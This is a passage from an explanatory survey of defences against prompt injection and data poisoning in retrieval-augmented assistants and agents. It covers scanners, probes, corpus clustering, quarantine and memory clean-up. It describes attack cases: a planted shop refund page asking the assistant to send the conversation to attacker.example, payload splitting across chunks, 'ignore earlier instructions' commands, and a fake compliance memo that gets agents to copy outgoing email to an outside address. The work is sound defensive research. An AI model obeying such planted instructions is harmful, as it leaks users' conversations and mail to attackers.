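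Munirathinam, who develops prompt-shield, also tried looser matching, borrowing a method biologists use to find related stretches of DNA. It lines up a text with known attack phrases and gives 3 points for an identical word, 2 for a listed synonym, and −1 for an unrelated or extra word. A three-word attack phrase scores 9 against itself. A paraphrase with two synonyms, one identical word and one extra word still scores 2 + 2 + 3 − 1 = 6. The method raised the number of attacks caught in the paraphrased set from 1 to 14 of 60. It also raised false alarms from 3 to 13 on 339 harmless texts, such as requests to see the instructions for something, that use words common in attacks.

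### Trained classifiers

A classifier also uses only the text, but it is trained on labelled examples instead of relying on a list. It is usually a small language model that outputs the probability that the text is an attack. It needs a few milliseconds per chunk on a graphics processor and can catch wording that nobody wrote a rule for. It can miss attacks unlike its training examples and flag harmless text that resembles an attack, and its score comes with no explanation.

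Meta's Prompt Guard, an 86-million-parameter classifier released in 2024, can raise many false alarms. (Dhouib and colleagues tested its successor, PromptGuard 2.) In *CleanBase*, Jin, Wang and colleagues (2026) ran Prompt Guard on six document collections, and it flagged 27.9% of the harmless documents on average. The rate was 0.3% on a collection of scientific papers and 57.5% on one drawn from Wikipedia. Encyclopedia articles contain few commands, so instructions in the text can't fully explain the false alarms. The classifier seems to have been unreliable on text unlike its training data, so operators should measure false alarms on their own documents before relying on a published figure.

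### A language model as judge

A judge is a general-purpose language model that receives the chunk along with a question from the developer, such as whether the text tries to give orders to an AI assistant. It can explain its answer, and the developer can change what it looks for by rewriting the question. Each scan requires a full model call. *DataSentinel* (Liu, Jia and colleagues, 2025) measured about 1.6 seconds per call for a model with 7 billion parameters on an older graphics card, compared with 15.3 seconds for the application's own model to complete its task.

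Liu and colleagues asked that model, Mistral 7B, whether texts contained any injected instructions. Across seven kinds of harmless text, it answered yes 89–100% of the time. Mistral 7B dates from 2023, and recent models do much better. *Hidden in Memory* (Pulipaka, Hlebik and colleagues, 2026) used language models to find and remove passages meant to plant false memories in an assistant. The best of these models, Gemma 4 26B, located the passages with a score above 0.96.

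A judge also has to read the planted text, so the text may influence the verdict, as it did with the language-model rerankers that Yin and colleagues tested. A pattern rule doesn't have this weakness because it only matches characters.

### The refund page under three scanners

The table shows the results of running a rule, a classifier and a judge on the attacker's "Refund policy" chunk from the kitchenware shop and on two harmless chunks. The verdicts and scores are invented for illustration. The rule matches either a verb meaning "send" near an address or a phrase about ignoring instructions, and the classifier flags any chunk that scores above 0.50. The judge receives both the chunk and the question for which the retriever returned it.

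| Chunk | Rule | Classifier | Judge |
|---|---|---|---|
| Planted page: refund rules, plus a request to send the conversation to attacker.example | Flag | 0.34, pass | Flag |
| Shop's returns page: customers should email a photo of the damage to the returns desk | Flag | 0.08, pass | Pass |
| Shop's advice on scams: quotes a typical attack phrase as a warning | Flag | 0.93, flag | Pass |

The rule flags all three because they share the same surface features. It can't distinguish the attacker's address from the shop's unless someone gives it a list of addresses. The classifier passes the planted page because most of the chunk reads like a real refund policy and the request is polite, but it flags the scam advice for quoting the kind of phrase it learned to associate with attacks. The judge gets all three right by considering what each passage is for. It flags the planted page because helping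 a customer with a broken kettle doesn't require sending the conversation to an outside address.

The judge could easily have been wrong, though, because many companies do send copies of complaints to an outside records service. Without information about which services the shop uses, a judge can't reliably tell a legitimate instruction from an injected one.

Combining the verdicts doesn't solve the problem either. If the shop withheld every chunk that any scanner flagged, it would lose all three. With a majority vote, it would still withhold the scam advice along with the planted page.

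### Who should follow the instruction, and for whose purpose?

A better scanner has to determine who an instruction is addressed to and whether following it fits the user's task. A travel policy's deadline for receipts is addressed to employees, so quoting it is part of the assistant's job. A request to copy the conversation to a stranger is addressed to the assistant and has nothing to do with the refund the user asked about.

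Neither test is enough alone. The EchoLeak email was worded as a request to the employee, so a scanner that checked only for text addressed to an AI would have passed it. Such a scanner would also flag legitimate instructions to the assistant, like the shop's rule about asking for a photo of the damage. Whether an instruction fits the task depends on the user, who may want the agent to summarise a setup guide or to carry it out. The same chunk can therefore need different verdicts for different questions, which a scan at upload can't provide.

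### Judging a chunk together with the question

*Context-Aware Prompt Injection Detection via Small Language Models in RAG Pipelines* (Rai, 2026) describes nokast-secureRAG, a scanner that sits between the retriever and the assistant's model. The scanner is a language model with about 0.5 billion parameters. It reads the user's query and the retrieved text together, writes a short line of reasoning, and labels the text as safe, suspicious or a malicious instruction.

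Larger models produced the small model's training data. A 35-billion-parameter model wrote and labelled 5,233 pairs of queries and texts, some harmless and some with planted attacks. A 120-billion-parameter model from a different family then labelled every pair without seeing the original labels. The two models' labels matched on 95.0% of the pairs, and Rai trained the small model only on those.

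In addition to an ordinary test on 659 pairs, Rai designed a "judgment-flip" test with 120 cases. Each case places the same sentence in two documents, one where it is legitimate and one where it hijacks the assistant. In Rai's example, a line about deleting all previous output is normal in a manual for a disk tool but suspicious in a news article. A scanner passes a case only if it labels both versions correctly. The table gives the results in percent and the processing time per text when the scanner handles many at once.

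| Scanner | Attacks flagged | Harmless texts flagged | Flip cases passed | Time |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Pattern rules | 68.8 | 12.9 | 17.5 | under 1 ms |
| Prompt Guard | 90.0 | 69.0 | 9.2 | 6 ms |
| ProtectAI's classifier | 88.8 | 7.0 | 54.2 | 13 ms |
| nokast-secureRAG | 99.4 | 2.6 | 75.0 | 37 ms |

Recall, the share of attacks a scanner flags, means little on its own. Prompt Guard caught 90.0% of attacks but almost never passed a flip case, because it usually flagged the legitimate version too.

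The evidence that the query matters is weaker than it looks in the table. When Rai hid the query on the ordinary test, recall fell only from 99.4% to 98.7% and false alarms rose from 2.6% to 3.8%. Pairing each text with an unrelated query raised false alarms to 8.5%, so the model does use the query, but most attacks were recognisable without it. The flip test isn't conclusive either, because the text around the sentence differs between the two versions, so a scanner could pass by reading only the document, as ProtectAI's classifier did in more than half the cases. Rai doesn't report the flip results with the query hidden.

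The labels in the flip test are also less certain than the others. The 120-billion-parameter model disagreed with at least one label in roughly half of the flip cases, so Rai scored the test with the first model's labels. Some of those labels may be wrong, or the cases may be hard even for a large model.

The same model wrote the training data and the test texts behind all of these figures, often using the same attack templates, so recall on real attacks will probably be lower. Rai's one test on outside data used 300 documents from PoisonedRAG, which state false facts and contain no instructions. The scanner flagged 0.7% of them, whereas the same small model had flagged 14.3% before training. Rai reasonably argues that the scanner was not built to find false facts. But the drop also shows that training on instructions made the model less likely to flag other kinds of poisoned text. An operator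 worried about a false returns address or bank account would need a separate way of checking facts.

A single scan took 293–404 milliseconds, mainly because the model writes out its reasoning first. Rai had aimed for under 100.

### Probes that measure a model's reaction

Abdelnabi, Fay and colleagues (2024), in *Get my drift?*, considered it too error-prone to define what counts as an instruction. Their method, TaskTracker, instead measures whether reading a text changes what a model takes its task to be. It works in four steps:

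1. The model reads the user's request alone, and the software records its activations, the internal numbers it computes, at the last token.
2. The model reads the request again, this time with the retrieved text, and the software records the activations at the last token again.
3. The software subtracts the first set of numbers from the second.
4. A simple classifier, or probe, decides from the difference whether the model has picked up another task.

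If a(·) stands for the recorded activations, the probe's input is

Δ = a(request + text) − a(request)

To make the signal clearer, the software adds a prompt asking the model to list the requests it is about to carry out. The software records the activations before the model writes anything, so the method doesn't depend on an accurate answer.

Abdelnabi and colleagues trained probes for six open models on texts with harmless extra tasks inserted, such as trivia questions, and tested them on texts that also included malicious requests. They scored the probes by AUC, the probability that a randomly chosen poisoned text scores higher than a randomly chosen clean one. Random guessing would give 0.5, and the best probes reached at least 0.99 on every model. AUC measures only how well a scanner ranks texts, so the number of false alarms still depends on the operator's threshold.

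In one of their experiments, the poisoned texts asked the model to answer a question, while the clean texts contained the same question as part of the prose, for example by saying that readers may wonder what the capital of France is and then giving the answer. Probes on the middle and later layers of the small model Phi-3 separated the two with an AUC of about 0.99, while probes on the early layers did little better than chance. So the model seems to distinguish questions meant for it from other questions, and a probe can detect the difference. The experiment didn't include commands meant for human readers, which fill a company's manuals.

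The signal was about equally strong whether or not the model obeyed the inserted task. It was weaker for some long attack texts, and Abdelnabi and colleagues suggest that a short command within ordinary prose creates a sharper contrast. On a harder private test set with long documents, several languages and subtle phrasing, AUC fell to 0.934, then rose to 0.989 after retraining on similar data.

TaskTracker requires extra passes through the model for each new text, although training a probe takes little compute. The greater obstacle is that it needs the model's activations, which a company renting a closed model can't access. Such a company could run the probe on a separate open model, but the probe would then measure that model's reaction rather than the rented model's. Probes also don't transfer easily between models. When Pulipaka and colleagues applied a probe trained on one model to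 another, the AUC was 0.48–0.54, which is chance level. Mathematically aligning the two models' activations beforehand raised the AUC to 0.74–0.85. An operator that changes models will therefore probably need to train a new probe.

### A test task that an injection disrupts

DataSentinel, a method by Liu and colleagues, also observes a model's reaction but needs only its output. It places an instruction before the text to be scanned and gives both to a separate detection model. The instruction is to repeat a secret key, such as seven random letters, and ignore the text that follows. DataSentinel passes the text if the output contains the key and otherwise flags it, because something in the text has probably kept the model from following the instruction.

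An ordinary language model isn't ideal for this because it may resist the injection and repeat the key anyway. Liu and colleagues therefore trained the detection model to be easier to hijack, which is safe because it has no tools or private data. The training also had to anticipate attackers who write text that hijacks the assistant but leaves the detection model undisturbed. Liu and colleagues expressed this contest as a minimax problem, in which one side minimises a quantity that the other side maximises. In slightly simplified form, the objective is

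min over g of { average of max over x of [ −ℓ(k, g(d, x)) − α·ℓ(y, f(t, x)) ] + β·(average of ℓ(k, g(d, c))) }

The symbols have these meanings:

- g is the detection model, d is the instruction to repeat the key, and k is the key.
- f is the assistant's model, t is its normal task, and y is the output the attacker wants from it.
- x is a poisoned text, and c is a clean one.
- ℓ is a loss, which is small when a model's output is close to the desired output.
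- α and β set how much weight the second and third terms get.

The simulated attacker chooses x to make both losses in the square brackets small, so that the detection model repeats the key and the assistant does what the attacker wants. Training then adjusts g to make the key disappear for poisoned texts but still appear for clean ones. The last term penalises false alarms. Solving the problem exactly is impractical, so the software alternates between improving the attack and improving the detection model. Three rounds took about three hours and cost $0.90 in rented computing. Each scan then requires one call to the detection model, which took 0.7 seconds with a 1-billion-parameter version.

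In Liu and colleagues' tests on seven language tasks, DataSentinel flagged at most 1% of clean texts and missed at most 7% of existing attacks. It was much weaker when the attacker's task was the same as the user's, for example when both tasks were to judge the mood of a review. The attacker then only has to distort the answer and needs no competing instruction.

DataSentinel also did much worse on document collections. Jin and colleagues planted documents containing a plain conditional command to give a certain answer when asked a certain question, and DataSentinel missed 69.8% of them. It missed 30.6% when the command also included an instruction to ignore earlier instructions. A likely explanation is that nobody asks the detection model the question in the condition, so the command never takes effect and the model keeps repeating the key, whereas a command to ignore instructions takes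 effect immediately. The request on the shop's planted page is also conditional, since it applies only before answering a refund question. Two of DataSentinel's creators, Jinyuan Jia and Neil Gong, also worked on the later study, so misuse of the method probably didn't cause the poor results.

### Comparing documents across the corpus

Jin and colleagues' own method, CleanBase, looks for groups of documents with unusually similar vectors. Attackers often plant several documents for the same question so that the retriever returns enough of them, and their shared purpose tends to make their vectors similar.

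CleanBase links each document to its ten nearest neighbours by cosine similarity. It then keeps only the exceptionally strong links, those above the threshold

τ = μ + 2.5σ

where μ is the average similarity of a sample of the links and σ is their standard deviation. If the average were 0.60 and the standard deviation 0.08, for example, only links above 0.80 would remain. CleanBase flags every group of at least three documents that are all still linked to each other. Leaving out the threshold step made it flag more than 99% of harmless documents.

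The researchers tested CleanBase against nine attacks on six collections, ranging from about 5,000 to 5.4 million documents. All nine attacks were meant to make the system give an answer the attacker had chosen, not to steal data. CleanBase flagged 1.6–1.9% of harmless documents on average, depending on the attack. The table shows the average share of planted documents that CleanBase missed.

| Attack | Missed (%) |
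|---|---|
| Plain command | 0.0 |
| Command to ignore earlier instructions | 0.3 |
| False claim that the task is finished | 0.8 |
| Combination of these | 0.0 |
| Mixed attack | 2.0 |
| GASLITEing, tuned to the retriever | 0.0 |
| PoisonedRAG without access to the retriever | 5.7 |
| Phantom, activated by trigger words | 16.5 |
| PoisonedRAG with access to the retriever | 34.2 |

CleanBase did worst on the last attack because the attacker tuned each document separately, which made the documents less alike. Since it doesn't look for commands, it can find false statements that an instruction scanner would pass. It took one minute to process about 58,000 financial documents, compared with 13 minutes for Prompt Guard and more than ten hours for DataSentinel.

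In a collection of 2.7 million Wikipedia passages, even a 1.8% false-alarm rate means removing about 48,000 harmless passages. This had little effect on ordinary questions, because other passages usually contained the same information. But on questions written specifically about documents that one of the tested scanners had wrongly flagged, the share of correct documents retrieved fell from 93.8% to 85.0%.

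Company drives could be harder for CleanBase than these public collections. An office often keeps the draft, the approved version and last year's version of the same policy, and CleanBase flags near-copies like these. Jin and colleagues didn't test it on a company drive.

CleanBase also cannot detect an attack that uses only one or two documents, so it is useful only against mass poisoning. The shop's attacker planted a single page, and Chang and colleagues got their tuned texts into the top results with one document per query.

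### Instructions that cross chunk boundaries

Most scanners check one chunk at a time, but the model receives all the retrieved chunks together. An instruction split across several chunks can therefore be complete in the model's context even though the scanner never checks all of it at once.

This can happen by accident. If the splitter cuts the planted refund page partway through its key paragraph, one chunk might end with a request to file a copy of the conversation, and the next might begin with the address. A rule that looks for a verb meaning "send" near an address would match neither chunk. Both chunks are about refunds, so the retriever may well return both.

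Scanning overlapping windows of text before splitting it fixes this case. If each window is w tokens long and starts s tokens after the previous one, every passage of up to w − s + 1 tokens lies entirely within at least one window. For example, 50-token windows that start every 25 tokens cover any instruction of up to 26 tokens, but the scanner processes about twice as many tokens as it would by scanning the text once.

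Overlap doesn't help when the pieces are far apart. *Agentic AI Security* (2025) describes an attack called payload splitting, in which the attacker spreads an instruction over several harmless-looking inputs that the model later combines. The survey's example is a hiring assistant that reads fragments scattered through résumés. *Divide and Inject* (2026) tests a version for long texts that uses two fragments, which look harmless or incomplete on their own, and a cue for the agent to combine them.

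The cue may be the easiest part to catch because it instructs the agent, even though it names no harmful action. But ordinary documents also refer readers to other passages, for example by telling them to follow the steps in an appendix, so a scanner that flagged every such reference would raise many false alarms.

Splitting an instruction across separately retrieved chunks also makes the attack less reliable. If two chunks each independently reach the model for half of the relevant questions, both reach it for only a quarter. Thornton's paired documents both had to rank in the top results, and under hybrid search they never did so together until the attacker retuned them.

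To catch split instructions, an operator can scan the assembled context as well as the separate chunks. This scan has to run for every question, because the combination of chunks changes. A short instruction is also harder to detect in the assembled context, because it contributes less to the overall score of a longer text. For example, if a scanner's score behaves like an average over tokens, and a 400-token chunk contains a 40-token instruction scoring 0.95 while the rest scores 0.05, the chunk scores (40 × 0.95 + 360 × 0.05) / 400 = 0.14, which looks harmless. In a context of five 400-token chunks where only this one contains an instruction, the score drops to about 0.07. A 50-token window containing the whole instruction scores (40 × 0.95 + 10 × 0.05) / 50 = 0.77.

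Real scanners don't simply average across the whole input, but Munirathinam notes that rules and classifiers still have difficulty when most of the text is harmless. Munirathinam therefore compared the writing style of neighbouring 50-token windows, because an injected passage usually has a different author from the text around it. This worked perfectly on test documents with attacks in capital letters, but caught nothing on a new set where the attacks matched the document's tone.

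Short windows are therefore better for finding a brief instruction in a long text, while the full context is better for finding one split into pieces. An operator who wants to catch both has to run both scans. Rai didn't test nokast-secureRAG on attacks spread over several chunks. TaskTracker reads the whole context and detected insertions at the beginning, middle and end of a text, but each of its test texts contained the injected task in one piece.

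## What happens to a flagged chunk, and what does quarantine cost?

A scanner's flag has no effect until the surrounding software acts on it. Usually the software quarantines the chunk, withholding it from the model's context but keeping it for review. Dropping one chunk from the search results is easy, but deciding where to scan, cleaning up text that got through earlier, and dealing with false alarms are harder. False alarms will probably far outnumber real attacks in an ordinary document collection.

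### Scanning documents as they enter

A scan at entry can keep a poisoned chunk out of the index. The operator must choose whether new documents wait for the result or become searchable during the scan. Xu, Zhou and colleagues (2026) measured both options in *Bounded Provisional Visibility*. Harmless documents took 6.3 seconds to become searchable when they had to wait for the scan, and 3 milliseconds or less when they didn't. But when documents didn't wait and the scanner fell behind, searches returned poisoned documents a median of 34 times per test.

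Their compromise is to make a new document searchable at once, hide it if it hasn't passed the scan by a deadline, and show it again if it passes later. This cut the median from 34 to 7. An unchecked document stays visible for at most T + δ, where T is the deadline and δ is the time the search software takes to apply a change. The timer has to run separately from the scanner. When the two shared a queue in a test with a heavy backlog, documents stayed visible for about 50 times the deadline.

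A six-second delay hardly matters for a refund policy, so the kitchenware shop should make new pages wait. The deadline is more useful for news feeds and similar sources. It limits only how long an unchecked document stays visible, so a poisoned document that the scanner wrongly passes remains until someone finds it.

Later checks may not make up for that mistake. *TriShieldRAG* (Mohanty, Patel and colleagues, 2026) describes a system that screens documents at entry, ranks retrieved ones by trust, and has three models vote on the answer. It reduced the success rate of PoisonedRAG's planted falsehoods from 79% to 1%. When the researchers changed the documents' formatting, the entry check passed all 500 of them, and the attack succeeded 62% of the time, up from 56% without any defence. The ranking and the vote both relied on the same poisoned passages, so they failed together. A second scan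 for injected instructions would probably add little if the same wording fooled both scanners.

### Scanning chunks as the retriever returns them

Scanning at retrieval covers documents added before the operator had a scanner, as well as live sources, such as web pages, that never go through an entry check. It also checks old text with the newest version of the scanner. However, it delays every answer. An assistant that handles 10,000 queries a week and retrieves five chunks for each needs 50,000 scans a week, although the software can reuse a stored result if the text hasn't changed and the scan doesn't depend on the question.

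An experiment on agents with long-term memory shows that scanning the user's message can't replace either of these checks. It also shows why an agent's notes need their own check.

### Scanning what the agent saves

Some agents keep a persistent memory, a store of notes they can read in later conversations. If an agent saves a planted instruction as a note, the instruction can outlast the conversation and the document it came from.

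Leong (2026) tested this in *Injection-Execution Dissociation* with a fake compliance memo in the corpus. The memo contained an instruction to send copies of all outgoing email to an outside "audit" address. In the first of four sessions, the user asked the agent to look up the company's compliance rules and save them. Two sessions of unrelated work followed, and the software wiped the conversation history each time. In the last session, the user asked for a draft of a project status email. The attack succeeded if the agent sent the attacker a copy.

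Leong tried six defences on nine open models, with 40 runs for each combination. The table gives the results for the seven models whose behaviour was consistent when Leong repeated the tests.

| Defence | Where it acts | Attack success (%) |
|---|---|---|
| None | – | 99.6 |
| Relevance filter | User's message | 100 |
| Injection scanner | User's message | 100 |
| The same scanner | Retrieved documents | 100 |
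| Small language model as judge | Retrieved documents | 100 |
| Stricter system instructions | Agent's instructions | 100 |
| No tool for reading saved notes | Agent's tools | 0 |

The two defences that checked the user's message did not scan the memo. Even a perfect scanner would have passed the user's message, because it was harmless.

The scanners at the retrieval stage received the memo but were too weak to detect it. Leong had built the classifier from only 60 examples, and the judge had 1.5 billion parameters. A judge with 7 billion parameters also missed the memo every time. When Claude Sonnet 4.6, GPT-5.1 and Gemini 2.5 Pro were used as judges, each flagged it in all 50 trials and raised no false alarms on harmless compliance documents. These results are encouraging, but the trials used only one memo and ten harmless documents.

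The agents' tools were simulated. The corpus held only three documents, so the agents almost always retrieved the memo. Leong also picked open models known to be vulnerable. In a separate test of 29 commercial models, seven leaked the email in at least nine of ten runs, and eleven leaked it less often. Most of Anthropic's models didn't save the instruction, or saved only a warning about it.

Three models, GPT-5.4, GPT-5.6-sol and Claude Haiku 4.5, never leaked anything in 40 runs each, but they hardly sent any email. Leong then supplied the content and asked each model 20 times to send the message. GPT-5.4 leaked it every time, Haiku 4.5 six times and GPT-5.6-sol five times. For GPT-5.6-sol and Haiku 4.5, the wording of the saved note seemed to matter. They leaked in 11 of the 17 runs where the note was a plain instruction, and in none of the 23 where it contained a warning, asked for verification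 or was missing. This is only a correlation, but it suggests that an agent should record outside text as something a document claimed, not as a rule.

None of the six defences checked the note when the agent saved it. *ElephantBroker* (Lupascu and Lupascu, 2026) describes a memory system of the same name that does, starting with pattern rules that take little compute and ending with trained classifiers. Lupascu and Lupascu tested whether the software works as designed, but not how many attacks it catches.

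Notes are hard to scan because the agent may have reworded a suspicious paragraph into a short note about company policy. This is another reason to copy a chunk's source label to every note made from it.

### The quarantine procedure

Suppose a scanner flags the attacker's "Refund policy" chunk while a customer waits for an answer. The shop's system could handle it as follows:

1. Withhold the chunk from this answer, and mark it in the index so that later searches skip it.
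2. Refill the gap with the next chunk in the ranking that passes the scan.
3. Log the question, the chunk's text and source, the scanner's version and score, and every earlier conversation that retrieved the same chunk.
4. Have a person review the chunk as plain text, with hidden characters visible.
5. Release the chunk if it is harmless, or delete it if it isn't.
6. Search for sibling chunks, such as the rest of the same document and anything else from the same account.
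7. Find and clear notes, summaries and other text that the system derived from the chunk.

The software can do the first three steps immediately, without waiting for a person. Refilling requires spare results, and Xu and colleagues calculate how many. If the assistant needs k chunks and the search returns αk, the assistant has too few when more than a fraction 1 − 1/α of the results are in quarantine. With k = 5 and α = 2, the search returns ten chunks, and the assistant has too few if six or more are in quarantine. That could happen if an attacker had planted many pages on the same subject.

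Staff can find a flagged chunk's siblings through the source details in the provenance wrapper. Xu and colleagues recommend the narrowest removal that the evidence supports. If a reseller's account is malicious, the shop should hide all of the reseller's pages, but if an attacker altered one page on an honest reseller's account, hiding them all would also remove many useful pages.

A deleted chunk may also survive in a backup, and restoring that backup would put the chunk back in the index. Xu and colleagues therefore keep a list of revoked chunks and apply it to every restored copy.

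### Clearing what the agent remembers

Clearing the agent's notes is the least reliable step. Four of Leong's open models saved the planted text under more than one name in nearly every undefended run. One of them, gpt-oss-20b, stored the forwarding rule in one note and the attacker's address in another, so deleting the rule left the address behind.

Clearing the notes also isn't enough while the memo is still in the corpus. When Leong removed the tool for reading notes, some models searched the corpus again and found the instruction. Mistral Large 3 still leaked the email in 39 of 40 runs, and GPT-5.1 did so in 74 of 99. Removing the search tool as well stopped every leak in tests on GPT-5.1 and GPT-4.1 mini. An operator should therefore quarantine the memo before clearing the notes, or the agent may find the instruction again.

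The text can also spread within the memory. *MemoryDojo* (Yang, Bullwinkel and colleagues, 2026) distinguishes persistence, where the original note survives, from propagation, where the agent writes the instruction into new or existing notes. For example, an agent that obeys a planted instruction may record what it did, creating a second copy that staff would miss if they deleted only the first note.

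In *MemSecBench*, Chen, Xie and colleagues (2026) measured how well agents clean up after such an attack. They wrote 310 cases in which an agent doing office work, coding or household tasks comes across malicious content. They ran each case on 24 setups, combining two agent frameworks, four memory systems and three models. On average, the malicious content stayed in memory in 84.2% of cases and led to the intended harm in 50.3%.

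The researchers then gave each poisoned agent a general clean-up request that didn't identify the bad memory. The agents removed or neutralised it in 86.3% of cases, but in many of those they damaged memories they should have kept. They removed the bad memory and kept all the required good ones in only 56.1%. The table gives this stricter success rate, in percent, for the setups that used GPT-5.5.

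| Memory system | OpenClaw framework | Hermes framework |
|---|---|---|
| Framework's own | 87.5 | 51.2 |
| Mem0 | 86.0 | 62.0 |
| Mem0-Graph | 86.7 | 35.0 |
| A-MEM | 93.3 | 24.0 |

The same model with the same memory system repaired 93.3% of cases in one framework and 24.0% in the other, so model quality is a poor guide to how well a system recovers. Chen and colleagues ran each case only once per setup and used a language model to judge most of the results. It agreed with human annotators about 91% of the time. An administrator with a log linking each note to its source should do better than an agent that has to guess which note is bad.

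### Withholding and refilling in a search test

*SearchInject* measured the first two steps of the procedure on a collection of 5,183 scientific abstracts. The researchers took 300 test queries and made four kinds of page for each, all containing an injected instruction:

- a page that repeats the query's main words in its title and opening sentence
- a "doorway" page that opens with a summary matching the query
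- a near copy of a relevant abstract with the instruction added at the end
- a page with the query's words in metadata that the search engine indexes

The system gives each of the top 100 results a risk score. It combines the page's relevance to the query (r), signs of search manipulation such as repeated words (a), and the likelihood that the text contains an instruction (i):

s = σ(b + β₁r + β₂a + β₃i + β₄ar + β₅ir)

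The function σ converts the sum to a number between 0 and 1, and the weights come from training. The last two terms let the warning signs count differently on highly relevant pages. The software goes down the ranking, skips every page that scores above 0.974, and stops when it has accepted ten pages. The researchers chose this threshold on separate data to catch as many planted pages as possible while withholding at most 0.5% of harmless results. On that data, the threshold caught 80% of the planted pages.

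In the table, exposure is the percentage of cases in which the planted page was among the ten results passed to the model. Ranking quality is a standard score from 0 to 1, measured on a clean copy of the collection.

| Search method | Exposure without defence | Exposure with quarantine | Change in ranking quality | Harmless results withheld |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Keyword search (BM25) | 94.1% | 15.8% | −0.0018 | 0.59% |
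| Both methods combined | 91.6% | 15.1% | −0.0013 | 0.62% |
| Older vector method (LSA) | 84.5% | 13.8% | −0.0013 | 0.65% |

Exposure fell by about five-sixths, and ordinary searches worked almost as well as before. The false quarantine rate was slightly above the 0.5% target, which can easily happen when an operator sets a threshold on one sample and applies it to another.

The instruction signal alone left exposure at 42%. The manipulation signals alone reduced it to 14% but lowered ranking quality by 0.11. The combined score did much better, but the comparison is rough because the researchers didn't set the three versions to the same false quarantine rate. It still suggests that a scanner in a search system should check how a page got into the results as well as what instructions it contains.

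Doorway pages were the hardest to catch and got through in 21–23% of cases. Refilling can also bring in a planted page that had ranked below tenth place.

The test was fairly easy in other ways. The same four kinds of page appeared in training and testing, nobody tried to write pages that would evade the score, and none of the search methods used a modern embedding model. The researchers also ran 104 attacks on two small language models. Quarantine removed the planted page in 83 of them, but the researchers couldn't confirm any hijacks even without the defence. The study therefore shows that quarantine reduced the number of planted pages reaching the model, but not how much it would reduce successful attacks.

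### Why most flags are wrong

A false quarantine rate of 0.6% sounds low, but poisoned chunks are probably much rarer than that. If π is the share of chunks that are poisoned, R is the scanner's recall and F is its false quarantine rate, the share of flags that are right is

πR / (πR + (1 − π)F)

Suppose one chunk in 10,000 is poisoned, recall is 0.8 and the false quarantine rate is 0.6%. In 10,000 chunks, the scanner flags 0.8 poisoned ones on average and 9,999 × 0.006, or about 60, harmless ones. So about 1.3% of the flagged chunks (0.8 of 60.8) are poisoned.

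The recall and false quarantine rate in this example are close to *SearchInject*'s results, but the share of poisoned chunks is an assumption, because there is no good measurement of it for company collections. Khodayari and colleagues' search of the open web found planted instructions on roughly one address in 100,000, and the true rate could be higher. The next table shows how much the same scanner's results depend on the share of poisoned chunks.

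| Poisoned chunks per 10,000 | Poisoned chunks flagged | Harmless chunks flagged | Share of flags that are right |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1,000 | 800 | 54 | 94% |
| 100 | 80 | 59 | 57% |
| 10 | 8 | 60 | 12% |
| 1 | 0.8 | 60 | 1.3% |

Published tests usually resemble the top row or contain even more attacks. Yin and colleagues tested scanners on one set where half of the documents carried attacks and on another, meant to be more realistic, where about one in ten did. Even if a scanner looks very accurate in such a test, almost all of its alarms in an office can be false.

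For a company with a million chunks, the bottom row means about 6,000 false alarms, 80 poisoned chunks caught and 20 missed. Reviewing the flagged chunks at two minutes each would take about 200 hours. Reviewers would see about 75 harmless chunks for every poisoned one, and would likely stop reading carefully. A poisoned chunk may also look like routine business procedure, so they could easily approve it by mistake.

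It makes sense to quarantine flagged chunks automatically even if only one flag in 75 is right. Withholding a chunk is reversible and often loses little information, because another chunk may contain the same facts. Deleting the chunk or blocking the supplier who wrote it should wait for stronger evidence.

A slower, more accurate scanner can shorten the queue by checking only the chunks the first one flagged. If it clears 95% of the harmless chunks and still flags 90% of the poisoned ones, about 3 harmless and 0.72 poisoned chunks per 10,000 remain, so about one flag in five is correct. However, overall recall falls from 0.80 to 0.72. This calculation assumes that the two scanners' mistakes are unrelated, which is optimistic if both were trained on similar examples.

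Reviewers can then start with chunks that come from outside parties, contain an outside address, or are retrieved for many questions. If the system saves each decision with a hash of the text, nobody has to review an unchanged chunk twice.

### Harmless text that looks like an attack

The 0.6% rate comes from scientific abstracts, which contain far fewer instructions than company documents. *Securing AI Agents Against Prompt Injection Attacks* (2025) reports that its defences flagged or filtered 5.7% of legitimate retrievals, mostly because of technical documents that describe system commands. *Defending Against Prompt Injection with DataFilter* (2025) describes a false alarm that occurred when a user asked an agent to add the ingredients for chocolate chip cookies to a grocery list. The recipe file had cooking steps under the heading "Instructions", and the filter mistook harmless text in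 the file for an attack.

Some scanners flag harmless text because of a single word. Li and Liu (2024), in *InjecGuard*, built a test called NotInject from 339 harmless texts, each containing one to three words common in attacks. The open-source scanners they tried scored below 60%, compared with 50% for guessing. One scanner flagged a question about whether it was safe to ignore a warning in some code, and its internal weights showed that it had relied almost entirely on the word "ignore".

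Li and Liu reduced the problem by retraining their scanner. They first gave it every word fragment in its vocabulary, one at a time. No single fragment can be an attack, so any that the scanner flagged revealed a bias. They then generated 1,000 harmless texts containing the flagged fragments and added them to the training data. The retrained scanner's accuracy averaged more than 83% across attacks, ordinary texts and NotInject.

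Newer models do much better on NotInject. *Safety Reconstructed* (2026) compared several general safety filters and found that LLaDA-Guard and ShieldGemma flagged none of the texts. The worst, Granite, flagged 1.8% of those with one trigger word and 10.6% of those with three. But a filter that can't detect injections would also get a perfect score, so operators need to check a filter's recall too. The test also consists of short messages, so it gives only a rough idea of how a scanner would treat a 300-page manual.

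### Correct answers lost

Wrongly withholding a chunk does the most harm when no other chunk contains the answer. *Prevented is Not Protected* (Dahal and Xiong, 2026) looked for this kind of damage by running the same questions with and without a defence. The defences were meant to stop planted falsehoods, and not all of them remove passages, but the results still show what to measure when testing quarantine.

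Without a defence, the system gave answers that a judge model rated correct on 92 of 200 clean questions from one standard set. With KeywordAgg, which asks the model about each passage separately and combines keywords from its answers, 56 of those 92 stayed correct, 17 became wrong, and the judge couldn't decide on 19. With TrustRAG, which filters passages and resolves conflicts between them, 23 stayed correct, 4 became wrong, and 65 were undecided. The judge agreed with human reviewers on correctness only about half the time when undecided cases counted as disagreements. Dahal and Xiong treat these figures as preliminary, and the figures are too uncertain to show which defence does less harm.

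A defence can also turn a safe answer into a harmful one. In 100 questions with one planted passage each, a simple text match suggested that TrustRAG had prevented 20 of the attacker's answers and caused 20 new ones. When Dahal and Xiong read the answers, they confirmed 16 of the prevented ones but only 6 of the new ones. In most of the rest, the model had mentioned the attacker's claim in order to question it. TrustRAG did more good than harm here, but counting only prevented attacks would have missed the harm.

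The shop could run a similar test by asking its assistant a fixed set of refund and delivery questions with quarantine on and off. If correct answers disappear, the shop can use the log to find which withheld chunks they depended on.

### Getting good documents withheld on purpose

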